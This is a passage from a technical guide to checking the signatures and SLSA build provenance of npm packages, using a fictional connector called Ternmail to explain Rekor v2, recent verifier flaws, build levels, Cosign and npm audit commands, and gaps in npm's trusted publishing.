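Sigstore's redesign of Rekor changes how clients establish the time of signing. The original Rekor returns a time from its internal clock with each entry. Rekor v2 does not, so the signer gets a signed timestamp from a separate service, according to Sigstore's *Rekor v2 GA*. This is an improvement because, according to the client specification, outsiders cannot verify the old log's clock.

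Rekor v2 stores its tree as static files called tiles, which are cheaper to serve than a database. It takes a few seconds to accept an entry because it adds entries in batches and returns the inclusion proof once the new entry is in the tree. The older version can return a signed promise of inclusion, which many clients accept in place of a proof. Rekor v2 no longer keeps copies of attestations, so the package registry's copy of a bundle is more important.

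Sigstore's configuration gives the first public v2 log a start date of 6 October 2025. Signing tools did not switch to it automatically at release because Sigstore wanted users to upgrade their verifiers first. Some projects have chosen to switch. NVIDIA's *Rekor v2 Signing* describes one of the company's open-source projects that now uses the new log by default. Sigstore has put the original version in maintenance mode and promised a year's notice before that log stops accepting entries.

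For now, users may encounter bundles from either log. Cosign supports v2 from version 2.6.0. The Go, Python and Java libraries supported it at release, with JavaScript and Ruby to follow. An old client may reject a valid v2 bundle, so a failed check is a reason to update the client and try again before suspecting Ternmail. The v2 design allows for witnessing, but this was only planned when Sigstore released v2.

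### Flaws in the checking software

A verifier protects the user only if it carries out each step correctly, and in 2026 researchers and maintainers disclosed several cases in which one did not. The worst was in the Ruby library sigstore-ruby, which compared the file's digest with the one in the attestation but reported success even when they did not match, according to NVD's *CVE-2026-31830* (2026). An attacker could have paired any genuine attestation with any file. The other checks did not help because none of them examines the file's contents, according to GCVE's *GHSA-mhg6-2q2v-9h2c* (2026). Version 0.2.3 fixed the flaw.

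Two flaws affected JavaScript libraries. OSV's *CVE-2026-48815* (2026) reports that the library silently ignored a setting that lets a program require particular certificate extensions, such as a given source repository. A program that relied on this setting to restrict a shared workflow to Ternmail's repository would have accepted packages from any other project that used the workflow. Version 4.1.1 of the `sigstore` package fixes this flaw. GitLab's *CVE-2026-48816* (2026) describes the other flaw, which let whoever supplied the bundle choose the signing time under certain conditions. This would mainly help someone who had also obtained a temporary key after its certificate expired.

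GitLab's *CVE-2026-22703* (2026) reports a flaw in Cosign's log check, which could accept a genuine Rekor entry unrelated to the file, signature or key being checked. An attacker would still need control of Ternmail's signing identity or key, but could then keep the malicious signature out of the log. Cosign's developers had fixed the same problem before, but a later code reorganisation brought it back. Version 2.6.2 contains the new fix, and users of Cosign 3 with default settings were never exposed.

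Other flaws affected fewer people. The Go library let users require entries in several independent logs, but GitLab's *CVE-2026-49834* (2026) reports that the library counted several entries from one log towards the total. Cosign requires only one log and was not affected. A separate flaw in how Cosign handled expired issuing certificates did not affect the public Sigstore service, according to Alpine Linux's *CVE-2026-24122*.

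None of these reports describes an actual attack, and most of the flaws needed unusual settings or an earlier break-in. But the reports show that a "Verified OK" result depends on the verifier's version, so anyone who pins a connector's version should still keep the verifier up to date.

### Who has to be trusted, and what monitoring adds

Even a flawless verifier relies on several services. Sigstore's *Threat Model* describes what happens if an attacker takes over any of these services or the signer's account.

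| Service or key | What an attacker who controlled it could do | What would limit the damage |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub's identity service | Issue tokens in Ternmail's name | The resulting certificates appear in a public log |
| Fulcio | Issue certificates in Ternmail's name without a token | Clients reject certificates that lack a promise from the certificate log |
| Certificate log | Promise to list a certificate and then leave it out | The attacker would also need a false certificate |
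| Rekor or the timestamping service | Confirm a false signing time, or hide an entry from some readers | The attacker would also need a signing key |
| TUF root keys | Replace the trusted keys of all the Sigstore services | Offline storage, and a rule that several keyholders must sign |

The identity provider matters most here. According to Sigstore's *Security Model*, Fulcio accepts a valid token as sufficient proof of identity. It has no other way to check whether Ternmail's workflow requested the certificate.

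Fulcio also has to obtain each provider's genuine keys. In June 2026, its developers disclosed a flaw in this step. For some providers, Fulcio followed redirects to other websites when looking up keys. A malicious or compromised provider could therefore make it store an attacker's keys, according to GitLab's *CVE-2026-49478* (2026). Version 1.8.6 fixed this flaw. A less serious flaw came from a pattern without anchors, a mistake users can also make with Cosign. NVD's *CVE-2026-22772* reports that it let attackers send requests to internal addresses through Fulcio, but not read the responses.

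In most of these cases the logs make the forgery visible to someone who checks them, but do not prevent it. Trail of Bits' *Catching malicious package releases using a transparency log* (2025) describes work on rekor-monitor, a program that checks that the log remains consistent and searches new entries for identities its user has listed. If an attacker signed a package as `ternmail/connector`, a monitor watching for that identity would notify Ternmail, which could compare the notice with its own release schedule. Without monitoring, someone would have to notice other traces, such as an odd tag or build record, which an attacker can hide.

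The notice arrives after the package has been signed, and perhaps after the first users have installed it. It is most useful when users observe a cooldown before installing new releases, because Ternmail then has time to withdraw the release. The notice looks the same for an attacker's release and an ordinary one if both come from the official workflow, so a person at Ternmail has to recognise that nobody planned the release.

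A user cannot easily find out whether Ternmail monitors the log, but the log is public, so a company that depends on the connector can check it for entries under Ternmail's identity. Trail of Bits provides a ready-made GitHub workflow for this. At the end of 2025, a hosted service with email alerts, like the existing one for Go packages, had only been suggested.

### Whether signing matters when the registry is secure

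If the npm registry works as intended, a signature might add little for a user who downloads from it over an encrypted connection. npm already requires publishers to log in, keeps records and supplies a digest.

Kalu and Davis (2025), in *Why Software Signing (Still) Matters*, accept part of this objection. They assume a well-defended registry and ask what happens to its protection as the package moves on. They distinguish cases by the number of parties involved. With only two, a developer handing a file directly to a user they know, a signature is optional. A central registry adds a third party, and signing can then be redundant for a direct download because the registry vouches for the publisher and the file at that moment. A mirror or a company's internal cache adds a fourth, and here they consider signing important.

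A registry's controls don't protect a package after it leaves the registry. Suppose that Ana's employer routes all npm downloads through its own cache. npm may have checked Ternmail's login carefully, but Ana's laptop connects only to the cache, and someone who breaks into the cache can replace the package. The same applies to a file that an administrator carries on a disk into a network with no internet connection. A signature travels with the file, so Ana can check it wherever she got the copy. She must get the trusted root and the expected identity from a separate source, but she doesn't have to trust the cache's operator.

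A digest gives some of the same protection. If Ana made her lock file from npm directly, she can use its digest to detect a cache that later serves a different file for version 1.4.2. The lock file can't help her check version 1.5.0, which she has never seen. Kalu and Davis add that a checksum identifies the content but not the publisher, so nobody is accountable for the file.

Kalu and Davis also doubt that registries are as secure as the objection assumes. In 2013 attackers broke into RubyGems.org, the registry for the Ruby language, and its operators had to rebuild the service and verify the packages. In 2016 the registry disclosed a bug that could have let attackers replace certain files. Kalu and Davis give reasons but no measurements, and these examples are old, but they show that the risk is real. The number of parties is also a rough guide, since four careful organisations may be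 safer than three careless ones.

Their account leaves out an advantage that Ternmail's user has even when downloading the package directly. An ordinary token identifies only the account that uploaded the package to npm, while provenance also links the package to a build.

Kalu and Davis extend the argument to AI agents that choose and install packages themselves. An agent could check signatures automatically before installing anything, which would record its decisions and make trusted publishers harder to impersonate. Their example of the danger, `solana-py`, is weaker than the argument. This package appeared on PyPI in 2022, posed as the legitimate `solana` library and stole cryptocurrency keys. Its author could have signed it under their own identity, and an agent that checked only for a valid signature would have installed it. Sigstore acknowledges that signing does not help someone who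 requests the wrong package. Before an agent installs connectors unattended, someone therefore needs to list the approved packages and the identities expected to sign them.

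## Reading a build attestation and judging the build platform

A successful signature check shows that Ternmail's workflow signed the statement in the bundle. The user still has to read the statement and compare it with what they would expect from a normal release. How much they can trust the statement also depends on the build platform, because a signature cannot show whether somebody interfered with the build while it was running.

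### The fields of a provenance statement

The statement has two main parts. The subject identifies the package, and the "predicate" holds information about it. npm uses the SLSA provenance format for the predicate. The table below shows what the decoded statement for Ternmail's release might contain, with long values shortened. The fields follow the sample in *feat* (DeHamer, 2023), the code change that moved npm to version 1 of the SLSA format. Some fields need to be compared with expected values, while others only help someone investigating a problem.

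| Field | What it records | Value for version 1.4.2 | Does a verifier compare it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| `subject` | The package's name, version and digest | `pkg:npm/%40ternmail/connector@1.4.2`, with the SHA-512 digest `9c41f0...` | Yes, with the requested package and the downloaded file |
| `predicateType` | The format of the predicate | `https://slsa.dev/provenance/v1` | Yes, exactly |
| `buildType` | How to interpret the parameters | `https://slsa-framework.github.io/github-actions-buildtypes/workflow/v1` | Yes, exactly |
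| `externalParameters` | The repository, workflow file and git ref | A `workflow` entry with `https://github.com/ternmail/connector`, `.github/workflows/publish.yml` and `refs/tags/v1.4.2` | Yes, every entry |
| `internalParameters` | Details that the platform set itself | The `event_name`, here `push`, and numeric identifiers for the repository (`700000001`) and its owner (`80000001`) | Not required |
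| `resolvedDependencies` | The source commit | `4e7d19c...` | Optional |
| `builder.id` | The platform that ran the build | `https://github.com/actions/runner/github-hosted` | Yes |
| `invocationId` | The particular run | The web address of run `9000000001`, first attempt | No, but it leads to the run's page |

The digests can look mismatched because npm writes the same value in two ways. The provenance has it in hexadecimal, as `9c41f0...`, while the user's record and lock file have it in Base64, as `sha512-nEHw...`. Verification tools convert between them automatically. Anyone comparing them by hand can convert the Base64 to hexadecimal by running `node -p "Buffer.from('...', 'base64').toString('hex')"` with the part after `sha512-` in place of the `...`.

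The build type matters because platforms arrange their parameters differently. The example in GitLab's *SLSA provenance specification* has the external parameters `source`, `entryPoint` and `variables`, but no `workflow` entry, so a verifier that expected GitHub's layout would look for the repository in the wrong place. npm's layout has also changed. GitHub's *Introducing npm package provenance* shows the original, which put the repository under `configSource` and the commit under `materials`, so a very old release may need different rules.

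External parameters are the inputs that someone outside the platform can choose. SLSA treats them as untrusted and recommends rejecting a statement that contains an unfamiliar one. The platform sets the internal parameters, so a user who trusts the platform doesn't need to check them. The two numeric identifiers are still worth recording, because if Ternmail gave up its GitHub account and a stranger registered the same name, the repository's address would look the same but the numbers would change.

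Despite its name, the `resolvedDependencies` field may not list all the libraries in the connector. In DeHamer's sample, its only entry is the source commit. Even at the highest Build level, SLSA requires only a best effort to make the field complete, so the user's lock file remains the better list of libraries.

### Comparing two releases with the expected values

The expected values, like the expected signing identity, must come from an independent source. SLSA describes several possibilities. The producer can publish them, or the package's name can determine its repository, as in Go. Otherwise, a user can accept the first release and check later ones for differences, which is called trust on first use.

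Ternmail's user already has the repository's name from the company's website. They could find the workflow's filename in Ternmail's release instructions or, if it isn't there, in the provenance of earlier versions. Using earlier provenance only works if those versions were genuine.

Suppose that the user has written down these expectations and checks version 1.4.2. A week later, version 1.4.3 appears.

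| | Expected | Version 1.4.2 | Version 1.4.3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Build type | GitHub Actions workflow, version 1 | Matches | Matches |
| Repository | `https://github.com/ternmail/connector` | Matches | Matches |
| Workflow | `.github/workflows/publish.yml` | Matches | `.github/workflows/test.yml` |
| Ref | `refs/tags/v` and the version number | `refs/tags/v1.4.2` | `refs/heads/fix-timeouts` |
| Builder | `https://github.com/actions/runner/github-hosted` | Matches | Matches |
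| Result | | Pass | Fail |

Version 1.4.3 has a valid signature and comes from Ternmail's repository, so a user who checked only the repository would accept it. An attacker with a stolen npm token and access to a contributor's GitHub account could have produced it by pushing a branch whose test workflow also publishes the package. If Ternmail had switched off ordinary tokens, npm would have rejected the upload, because the trusted publishing entry names `publish.yml`. The change may also be innocent, such as a developer releasing an urgent fix in an unusual way. In either case, the user should stay on 1.4.2 until Ternmail explains the change.

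The commit is not among the values that SLSA tells verifiers to compare, since it changes with every release. It still allows a useful extra check. In some projects, people who cannot change the main branch can create tags, so a tag with a normal name may point to code that never went through the usual process. In an up-to-date copy of Ternmail's repository, this command tests whether the commit belongs to the main branch:

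```
git merge-base --is-ancestor 4e7d19c origin/main && echo "on main"
```

If a project maintains older versions on separate branches, legitimate releases from those branches will fail this test, so the user needs to know which branches Ternmail releases from.

Some influences on a build do not appear in the statement. A GitHub workflow can accept inputs from the person who starts it by hand, and npm's provenance does not list them. If `publish.yml` had an input for the mail server's address, someone with permission to start the workflow could enter an attacker's server. The provenance would still show the correct repository, workflow, ref and commit, but `event_name` would be `workflow_dispatch` (a manual start) instead of `push`. SLSA requires a complete list of external parameters only at Build level 3.

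### What the Build levels promise

The comparisons depend on the platform recording the values correctly and keeping outsiders from changing the build. SLSA's Build levels grade how well a platform does this. Version 1.2, released in November 2025, left the three levels unchanged from version 1.1 (SLSA, 2025).

| Level | What it requires | What it is meant to stop |
|---|---|---|
| Build level 1 | Provenance exists, possibly without a signature | Mistakes, such as a release from a commit that is missing from the official repository |
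| Build level 2 | A hosted platform generates and signs the provenance | Tampering after the build |
| Build level 3 | The platform also isolates builds and keeps signing secrets away from them | Tampering during the build |

At level 1, a Ternmail developer could build the connector on a laptop and attach an unsigned description of the build. The description would help a colleague find out which commit went into a release, but an attacker could write an equally convincing one.

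Level 2 stops an attacker who breaks into a download server and changes the package, because the package no longer matches the digest in the signed provenance, and editing the provenance would invalidate its signature. According to SLSA, forging provenance at this level may still be easy for someone who deliberately attacks the build, but level 2 should deter people with something to lose, such as an employee who would be dismissed if caught.

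Level 3 is meant to protect against an attacker who can already run code in or near the build, perhaps through a malicious library or another workflow in the same project. To forge provenance, this attacker should have to exploit a flaw in the platform that most attackers could not. Level 3 does not protect against a dishonest employee of the platform, so users still have to decide whether they trust GitHub.

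The provenance does not include the SLSA build level. A verifier looks up the signer and `builder.id` in its own list of trusted platforms, which gives the highest level it accepts for each. In SLSA's example list, one platform claims level 3, but the verifier trusts it only to level 2. Provenance from an unknown platform counts as level 1 at most, regardless of any claim to a higher level. Several reports on the 2026 attack on TanStack, a family of JavaScript packages, overlooked this and described valid npm attestations as level 3.

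Older documents may use the level numbers differently, because SLSA's first draft had a single scale from 1 to 4 that mixed source and build requirements. Current claims should therefore use "Build level 3" rather than just "SLSA 3". There is no Build level 4 yet, though the SLSA project is considering one that might require a complete record of a build's inputs.

### Isolation at level 3

SLSA distinguishes between the build environment, where the project's own script runs, and the control plane, the part of the platform that starts builds and records them. A project may run any code in its build environment. Ternmail's workflow, for example, runs code by dozens of outside developers when it installs libraries and runs tests. The isolation rules limit what that code can reach.

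Build platforms often keep downloaded or half-finished files in a cache so that the next build can start faster. Level 3 forbids cache poisoning, in which one build tampers with cached files that another build uses, by requiring a build's output to be the same with or without the cache. Suppose Ternmail has a second workflow that tests changes proposed by strangers and shares a cache with the release workflow. A stranger could propose a change that replaces the cached copy of the mail-parsing library. The next release would include the altered library, even though the release's provenance would correctly name the official commit.

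GitHub made this attack harder in June 2026 by preventing less trusted workflows from changing the cache they share with others. SLSA's rule goes further because it also applies between trusted builds in one project. If Ternmail had a nightly workflow that could still write to the shared cache, an attacker who took over that workflow could poison the release.

Another rule requires the platform to keep its signing secrets away from the build. Otherwise, a malicious library in Ternmail's build could steal the signing key and sign a false statement about a different file. The control plane therefore has to hold the key and generate or check every field except the name and digest of the finished file.

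An attacker gains little by using that exception to supply a false digest. Suppose the attacker falsely claims that a build in their own repository produced Ternmail's genuine package. The resulting statement links a good file to the wrong repository, so the user rejects it.

A build must also leave nothing behind that affects later ones. In SLSA's example, an attacker's build replaces `make`, a common build tool, and the next project built on the same machine uses the altered version. Giving every build a fresh machine prevents this. GitHub's hosted machines work this way, but a project may also connect its own machine, which can keep files between builds. This is one reason to check that `builder.id` ends in `github-hosted`.

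The same isolation applies to builds that run at the same time. If a platform lets people log in to a running build to fix problems, it has to record that access as an external parameter so that a verifier can detect it.

SLSA requires only that a well-intentioned build runs without interference, so a careless build can still be unsafe. Ternmail's script could download a program from an unprotected website and add it to the package, and the platform could still qualify for level 3.

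### Why npm's built-in provenance stays at level 2

A package released through GitHub Actions with npm's built-in provenance is built on a hosted platform and has signed provenance, which SLSA rates as Build level 2. It doesn't reach level 3 because npm signs the provenance on the build machine. It requests the OIDC token and creates the temporary signing key there, within reach of any other code in the job.

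The design does not quite fit level 2. Under SLSA, the control plane should generate the provenance, but npm's program writes the statement inside the build environment. The certificate makes up for much of this, because npm rejects a statement that does not match it. Code inside Ternmail's build can alter the statement, but it cannot change which repository the certificate names.

Engineer in Tokyo's *Understanding GitHub Artifact Attestations*, a blog post about GitHub's separate attestation service, reports that some people call a similar arrangement "SLSA Build L2+". GitHub's service also signs inside the build job, and its verifier relies on the certificate instead of the statement. The post points out that an attacker can copy the temporary key out of the build and use it elsewhere during the certificate's ten-minute lifetime, and that code in the build can tamper with information that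 isn't in the certificate, such as a workflow's inputs.

Level 2 is still useful to Ternmail's users because someone who publishes a lookalike package cannot obtain provenance that names `ternmail/connector` without first getting into Ternmail's repository or build. Level 2 offers little resistance to an attacker who has got that far.

### Moving the build into a shared workflow

On GitHub, projects usually reach level 3 with a reusable workflow, a script that other workflows can call. Its jobs run on separate virtual machines from the calling workflow's jobs. SLSA's *Bringing improved supply chain security to the Node.js ecosystem* (2023) announced a test version of such a workflow for npm packages. The workflow builds the package on one machine and generates and signs the provenance on others, so a malicious library that runs during the build cannot reach the signing key.

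GitHub calls the use of a reusable workflow the "critical difference" between levels 2 and 3, but this is true only if the workflow is built carefully. GitHub's instructions put the build and attestation steps in the reusable workflow, which prevents the calling workflow from interfering with them. A malicious library could still reach the signing key if those steps ran in the same job. A reusable workflow would also break the cache rule if it restored files that other workflows can change.

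It also matters who controls the shared workflow. If Ternmail wrote a reusable workflow and kept it in `ternmail/connector`, anyone who could change `publish.yml` could probably change that file too. If Ternmail instead calls a workflow that Buildguild, a fictional group, maintains for hundreds of projects, a Ternmail developer can no longer change how the provenance is generated, but an intruder at Buildguild could affect every project that uses the workflow. SLSA describes this as moving the root of trust rather than removing it.

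A shared workflow also saves verifiers work. In the discussion *[feature] Comparison to new GitHub Artifact Attestations?*, a contributor argues that level 3 has to hold regardless of the project. Otherwise a verifier would have to inspect the build workflow of every dependency.

The user then has to check two names, because the signing identity belongs to Buildguild's workflow while the source repository is Ternmail's. If the workflow also stores its attestation with GitHub, GitHub's command-line tool can check both:

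```
gh attestation verify connector-1.4.2.tgz \
  --repo ternmail/connector \
  --signer-workflow buildguild/workflows/.github/workflows/npm-release.yml
```

Without the second option, the tool accepts only a signing workflow from Ternmail's repository, so it rejects the package. A user who sees this failure should find out who maintains the shared workflow before adding its name to the command.

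Few small projects are likely to make this change soon. Engineer in Tokyo recommends it but notes that passing files between separate jobs makes the setup harder. For now, most attested npm connectors will probably offer level 2.

### How the commit got into the repository

Build provenance identifies the source commit but does not record how that commit was accepted. SLSA 1.2 adds the Source Track, which grades how well source code is protected, separately from the build.

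| Level | What it requires | What it would mean for Ternmail |
|---|---|---|
| Source level 1 | A version control system | Every commit has a fixed identifier |
| Source level 2 | A preserved history and signed records of each change | Nobody can erase a malicious commit or move the tag `v1.4.2` to other code |
| Source level 3 | Continuous enforcement of the project's own rules | If Ternmail requires tests before a change, nobody can skip them |
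| Source level 4 | Review by two trusted people | One employee cannot add code alone |

The signed records are called source provenance. The hosting service creates them at the time of the change, and they show who made it and which rules applied. A commit's author line is much weaker evidence, because anyone can type another person's name there.

Continuity matters because a project's administrators can usually switch its rules off. One of them could disable the review requirement, add a harmful commit and re-enable the requirement a minute later, and the settings page would look normal afterwards. Under the Source Track, the gap ends the period for which the project can claim that rule, and a new period starts with a later commit. Projects also make no claim about code from before they adopted the rules.

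Source level 4 would have stopped the Ternmail employee who added a line to copy customers' mail, unless a colleague had approved the change. SLSA acknowledges that it does not address reviewers who approve changes without reading them, two people who collude, or harmful code that looks harmless. Projects may also let trusted bots make changes without a second reviewer, and an attacker could try to take over one of these bots.

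A user can combine the two tracks by matching commits. The build provenance links version 1.4.2 to commit `4e7d19c`, and a source attestation for the same commit would show how it reached the main branch. The hosting service has to issue source attestations, and SLSA's sample configuration still refers to a GitHub workflow labelled "poc", for proof of concept. Most connector users are therefore unlikely to find a source attestation yet, and can only check the commit's review history on GitHub, which lacks the signature an attestation would have.

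### Letting one verifier report for many users

Checking all this for a connector and a hundred dependencies is too much work for each employee of a company. SLSA's answer is the verification summary attestation (VSA), in which one verifier reports the result of its checks. The security team at Ana's company could examine Ternmail's package once and sign a statement with the package's digest and this predicate:

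```json
{
  "verifier": { "id": "https://security.example.com/connector-checks" },
  "resourceUri": "https://registry.npmjs.org/@ternmail/connector/-/connector-1.4.2.tgz",
  "policy": { "uri": "https://security.example.com/connector-policy" },
  "verificationResult": "PASSED",
  "verifiedLevels": ["SLSA_BUILD_LEVEL_2"]
}
```

Ana's laptop then checks the team's signature, the digest, the verifier, the result and the level. It also has to compare `resourceUri` with the address of the package she requested. Otherwise, an attacker who controlled the company's package cache could replace Ternmail's connector with another package that had passed the checks and supply that package's valid summary.

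`verifiedLevels` can also include a Source level, or the result of a check that has no level, such as whether two independent platforms produced the same file. A company that sells closed-source software can use a summary to vouch for a build without publishing the details.

A summary may also count the package's dependencies at each SLSA level. SLSA derives that count from `resolvedDependencies`, which for an npm package typically contains only the source commit. Ana's security team would do better to issue a summary for each package in her lock file. Many of those packages will have no provenance, and the team has to decide in its policy whether to accept them anyway.

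Ana now depends on the team's policy and the security of its signing key. An attacker who took over the verifier could approve any package for the whole company, and the laptops would accept it without checking Ternmail's provenance.

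## Checking a connector published on npm

Ana or her company's security team may find three signed records on npm for Ternmail's connector. Users often confuse them, partly because one npm command checks all three.

| Record | Who signs it | What it proves | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|---|
| Registry signature | npm, for every version | The file is the one that npm hosts under this name and version | Who built it, and from what |
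| Publish attestation | npm, for versions with provenance | npm accepted this version from someone with permission to publish | Whether that person stole the permission |
| Provenance attestation | The build workflow, through Sigstore | Which repository, commit and workflow the package came from | Whether that is the right repository, and what the code does |

The registry signature covers one line of text with the package's name, version and digest. For Ternmail, the line would be `@ternmail/connector@1.4.2:sha512-nEHw...`. According to npm's *About registry signatures*, the signature protects against an attacker who controls a mirror or proxy and alters the package there. Nesbitt (2026), in *Signing and Attestations Across Package Registries*, points out that the registry also signs a release uploaded by a thief with a stolen token, just as it would a genuine one. The signature also can't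 show that npm itself didn't alter the file. npm told users "You still have to trust us" when it introduced an earlier version of these signatures.

The two attestations normally appear together. Ternmail's workflow signs the provenance and uploads it with the package. If npm accepts both, it signs the publish attestation with its own key and records it in Rekor, according to *Details on npm provenance*. The publish attestation helps if Ternmail's workflow builds and signs a version that npm then rejects. A dishonest mirror could offer that unreleased version to users with valid provenance, but it would have no publish attestation. However, npm treats a thief with a working token as an authorised user, so a publish attestation does not prove that Ternmail intended the release.

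### Fetching and verifying the evidence

Ternmail is fictional, so these commands use `semver`, a real package for comparing version numbers. Sigstore uses its version 7.6.3 as an example. The first three fetch the package and its provenance:

```
curl -O https://registry.npmjs.org/semver/-/semver-7.6.3.tgz

curl https://registry.npmjs.org/-/npm/v1/attestations/semver@7.6.3 \
  --output attestations.json

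jq '.attestations[]
    | select(.predicateType | startswith("https://slsa.dev/provenance/"))
    | .bundle' attestations.json > semver-provenance.json
```

npm returns both attestations in one response, and `jq`, a tool for processing JSON, picks out the provenance. Ternmail's package name contains an `@` and a slash, which need encoding in the second address, so the last part would be `%40ternmail%2Fconnector@1.4.2`.

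The downloaded file is a second copy of the package. The copy that the AI application will run may have come through a company cache, so the user should check that both have the same digest. This command prints the digest of the download in the format that the lock file uses after `sha512-`:

```
openssl dgst -sha512 -binary semver-7.6.3.tgz | openssl base64 -A
```

The next command is `npm audit signatures`, which works only in a folder where `npm install` or `npm ci` has already installed the packages. The folder that Ana created for her lock file is suitable. For Ternmail's connector and its dependencies, the output might be:

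```
audited 101 packages in 2s
101 packages have verified registry signatures
9 packages have verified attestations
```

For each attestation, npm carries out the Sigstore checks described earlier. It also requires at least one attestation signed with npm's own key. But the command has no option for specifying which repository the user expects. If a thief had published version 1.4.2 from `ternmail-tools/connector`, the output would still show nine verified attestations.

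The output also doesn't show which nine packages have them. In npm 12, npm documents an option that adds the verified packages and their bundles to the JSON output, and `jq` can reduce this to a list of names:

```
npm audit signatures --json --include-attestations \
  | jq -r '.verified[] | "\(.name)@\(.version)"'
```

Neither form of the command can detect later changes to the installed files, because the digest covers the compressed package, not the unpacked folder.

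Cosign makes the comparison that npm's command leaves out. For `semver`, the user states that the package should come from the `npm/node-semver` repository and its release workflow:

```
REPO="https://github.com/npm/node-semver"

cosign verify-blob-attestation \
  --certificate-identity-regexp="^$REPO/.github/workflows/release-integration.yml@" \
  --certificate-oidc-issuer="https://token.actions.githubusercontent.com" \
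  --new-bundle-format --bundle semver-provenance.json \
  semver-7.6.3.tgz
```

If every check succeeds, Cosign prints `Verified OK`. This pattern accepts any branch or tag, unlike the exact identity shown earlier for Ternmail.

### What success and failure look like

The last command is worth running once with a deliberate mistake, such as `npm/cli` in place of `npm/node-semver`. Cosign then exits with an error about the certificate's identity instead of printing `Verified OK`. The package and its signature are still genuine, but they don't come from the repository named in the command.

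| Situation | `npm audit signatures` | Cosign with an expected identity |
|---|---|---|
| Provenance from the expected repository | Counts the package among the verified attestations | `Verified OK` |
| No attestation | No error, but the count is one lower | An error, because the bundle file is empty |
| Valid provenance from another repository | Counts the package among the verified attestations | An error about the certificate's identity |

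npm's documentation is inconsistent about missing attestations. The page on viewing provenance warns that the command returns an error if a package has missing attestations. Yet npm's sample output, described earlier, reports no error although most of the packages have none. The sample is more plausible, since the command would otherwise fail for almost every project. To find out whether one package has provenance, the user can run:

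```
npm view @ternmail/connector@1.4.2 dist.attestations
```

This prints an address and the type of provenance if npm has any, and nothing if it doesn't.

`npm audit signatures` reports an error when a package has no registry signature, because npm signs everything it hosts. npm warns that a missing signature might mean an attacker is trying to get around the check. In the example in npm's *Verifying registry signatures*, 235 of 1,640 packages have no signature, and the command lists them by name.

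An old copy of npm may cause an "invalid attestations" error. In *Run npm audit signatures*, a GitHub user reported in 2024 that seven of a project's 552 packages had invalid attestations, including the widely used `axios`. The suggested fix was to update npm. npm also recommends using its latest version to run `npm audit signatures`, which is often newer than the version included with Node.js. If the error remains after an update, users should not run the package.

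### What the website's check mark leaves out

npm's website shows a green check mark next to the version number of a package with provenance. Clicking on it leads to the build details described earlier. They are a convenient way to look at an unfamiliar connector, but the mark itself shows only that provenance exists. A lookalike package that an attacker built in their own public repository gets the same mark.

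The mark also applies to only one version of one package. Ternmail's page could have it while 92 of the connector's 100 dependencies have no provenance. It also can't show whether the copy on Ana's laptop is the file npm hosts.

Unlike the commands above, the npm website looks for the source commit and repository whenever someone opens the provenance details, and displays an error if it can't find them. This can happen when the owner deletes the repository or makes it private. The signatures remain valid, so Cosign would still print `Verified OK`, but nobody outside the project could read the code any more.

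The ordinary repository link on a package's page is unverified and leads to no particular commit, as GitHub explained when it introduced provenance.

### What npx checks before it runs a connector

npx performs none of these signature checks. It only compares the download with the digest in npm's metadata. The npm documentation for npx, as it stood on 4 December 2026, lists no option for checking a registry signature, an attestation or a repository. Nor can the user easily run `npm audit signatures` in between, because npx starts the connector as soon as it has installed it.

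npm also appears to have no setting, as of December 2026, that refuses packages without provenance. There is a setting called `provenance`, but according to npm's *Config* it applies to publishing. A user who sets it to `true` in the hope of stricter installations gets no extra protection. None of the changes in GitHub's 2026 review of npm's defences makes provenance a condition of installing, either. pnpm, an alternative to npm, can at least block a version whose evidence is weaker than that of earlier ones, according to Rush Stack's *PnpmOptionsConfiguration.trustPolicy property*.

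npm 12 does refuse some packages for other reasons. By default, it no longer fetches dependencies directly from Git repositories or from arbitrary web addresses, as GitHub announced in July. Such dependencies bypass the npm registry, so they have no registry signature or npm attestation to check.

Ana therefore has to check the connector before she edits the AI application's configuration. She installs it in its own folder, then runs `npm audit signatures` and Cosign. If both succeed, she points the configuration at the installed file. She needs to repeat the checks only when she updates the connector or one of its dependencies.

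### How npm decides which workflow may publish

Ternmail uses trusted publishing, so the next question is which workflow runs npm would accept as Ternmail's. A trusted publishing entry for GitHub has these fields, according to npm:

| Field | Ternmail's value | Required? |
|---|---|---|
| Organisation or user | `ternmail` | Yes |
| Repository | `connector` | Yes |
| Workflow filename | `publish.yml` | Yes |
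| Environment | (empty) | No |

When a workflow tries to publish, npm compares the OIDC token with these fields and issues a short-lived credential if they match. The fields do not include the branch or tag.

Suppose a contributor to Ternmail can create branches but cannot change the main one. The contributor pushes a branch called `fix-timeouts` on which `publish.yml` builds and publishes a malicious package. The organisation, repository and filename all match, so npm accepts it. SafeDep's *Trusted Relationship* records abuse of this rule in 2026. The malicious release's provenance would be accurate, and it would show `refs/heads/fix-timeouts` where the user expects a version tag, so comparing the git ref would catch the release.

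Ternmail can close the gap by naming a GitHub environment in the optional field. An environment is a named group of settings for a workflow's jobs, and a project can restrict it to certain branches. Arrange Act Assert's *The trusted publishing setting that would have blocked the npm snapshot-branch attacks* recommends an environment called `release` that only the main branch may use. A workflow on `fix-timeouts` then can't get a token with that environment's name, so npm rejects the upload.

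This works only if all of a package's entries require the environment. A package can have up to ten, and a match with any one of them is enough, according to GitHub. If Ternmail adds a second entry for test versions and leaves its environment empty, an attacker can use that one. Users can't check this, because npm lists the entries only for people with write access to the package.

The workflow name that npm checks can also differ from the one in the signing identity. If `publish.yml` calls Buildguild's shared workflow, npm checks the caller's name, `publish.yml`, while the Sigstore certificate names Buildguild's workflow. Both are correct, but a user who knows only one of them could mistake the other for a sign of tampering.

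A security report called SlugFest showed that, until recently, npm tied an entry to the repository's name instead of its permanent numeric identifier. A stranger who registered an account name that Ternmail had given up could therefore have matched the entry. npm now ties an entry to the permanent identifier at the first successful publication. Smith (2026) reports in *npm Puts a 48-Hour Clock on Unused Trusted Publishing Configurations* that an entry expires if nobody uses it within 48 hours. Nesbitt adds that npm rejects uploads from workflows triggered by a comment on an issue, since anyone may be able to comment on a public repository.

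Stored tokens continue to work for a package with a trusted publisher entry until a maintainer selects "Require two-factor authentication and disallow tokens" in the package's settings. GitHub's *npm trusted publishing with OIDC is generally available* (2025) gave the impression that such a package accepts releases only from the named workflow. Datadog Security Labs' *Decoding the GitHub recommendations for npm maintainers* (2026) warns that trusted publishing can also create a false sense of security, because it moves part of the responsibility to the build platform. The project still has to control who can create branches and start builds.

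### Which connector authors can't provide provenance

npm checks provenance before it accepts a release. The certificate has to show a supported build service, a machine that the service hosts and a public source repository. The statement has to agree with the certificate and contain the right name, version and digest. Finally, the `repository` line in `package.json` has to match the repository in the certificate.

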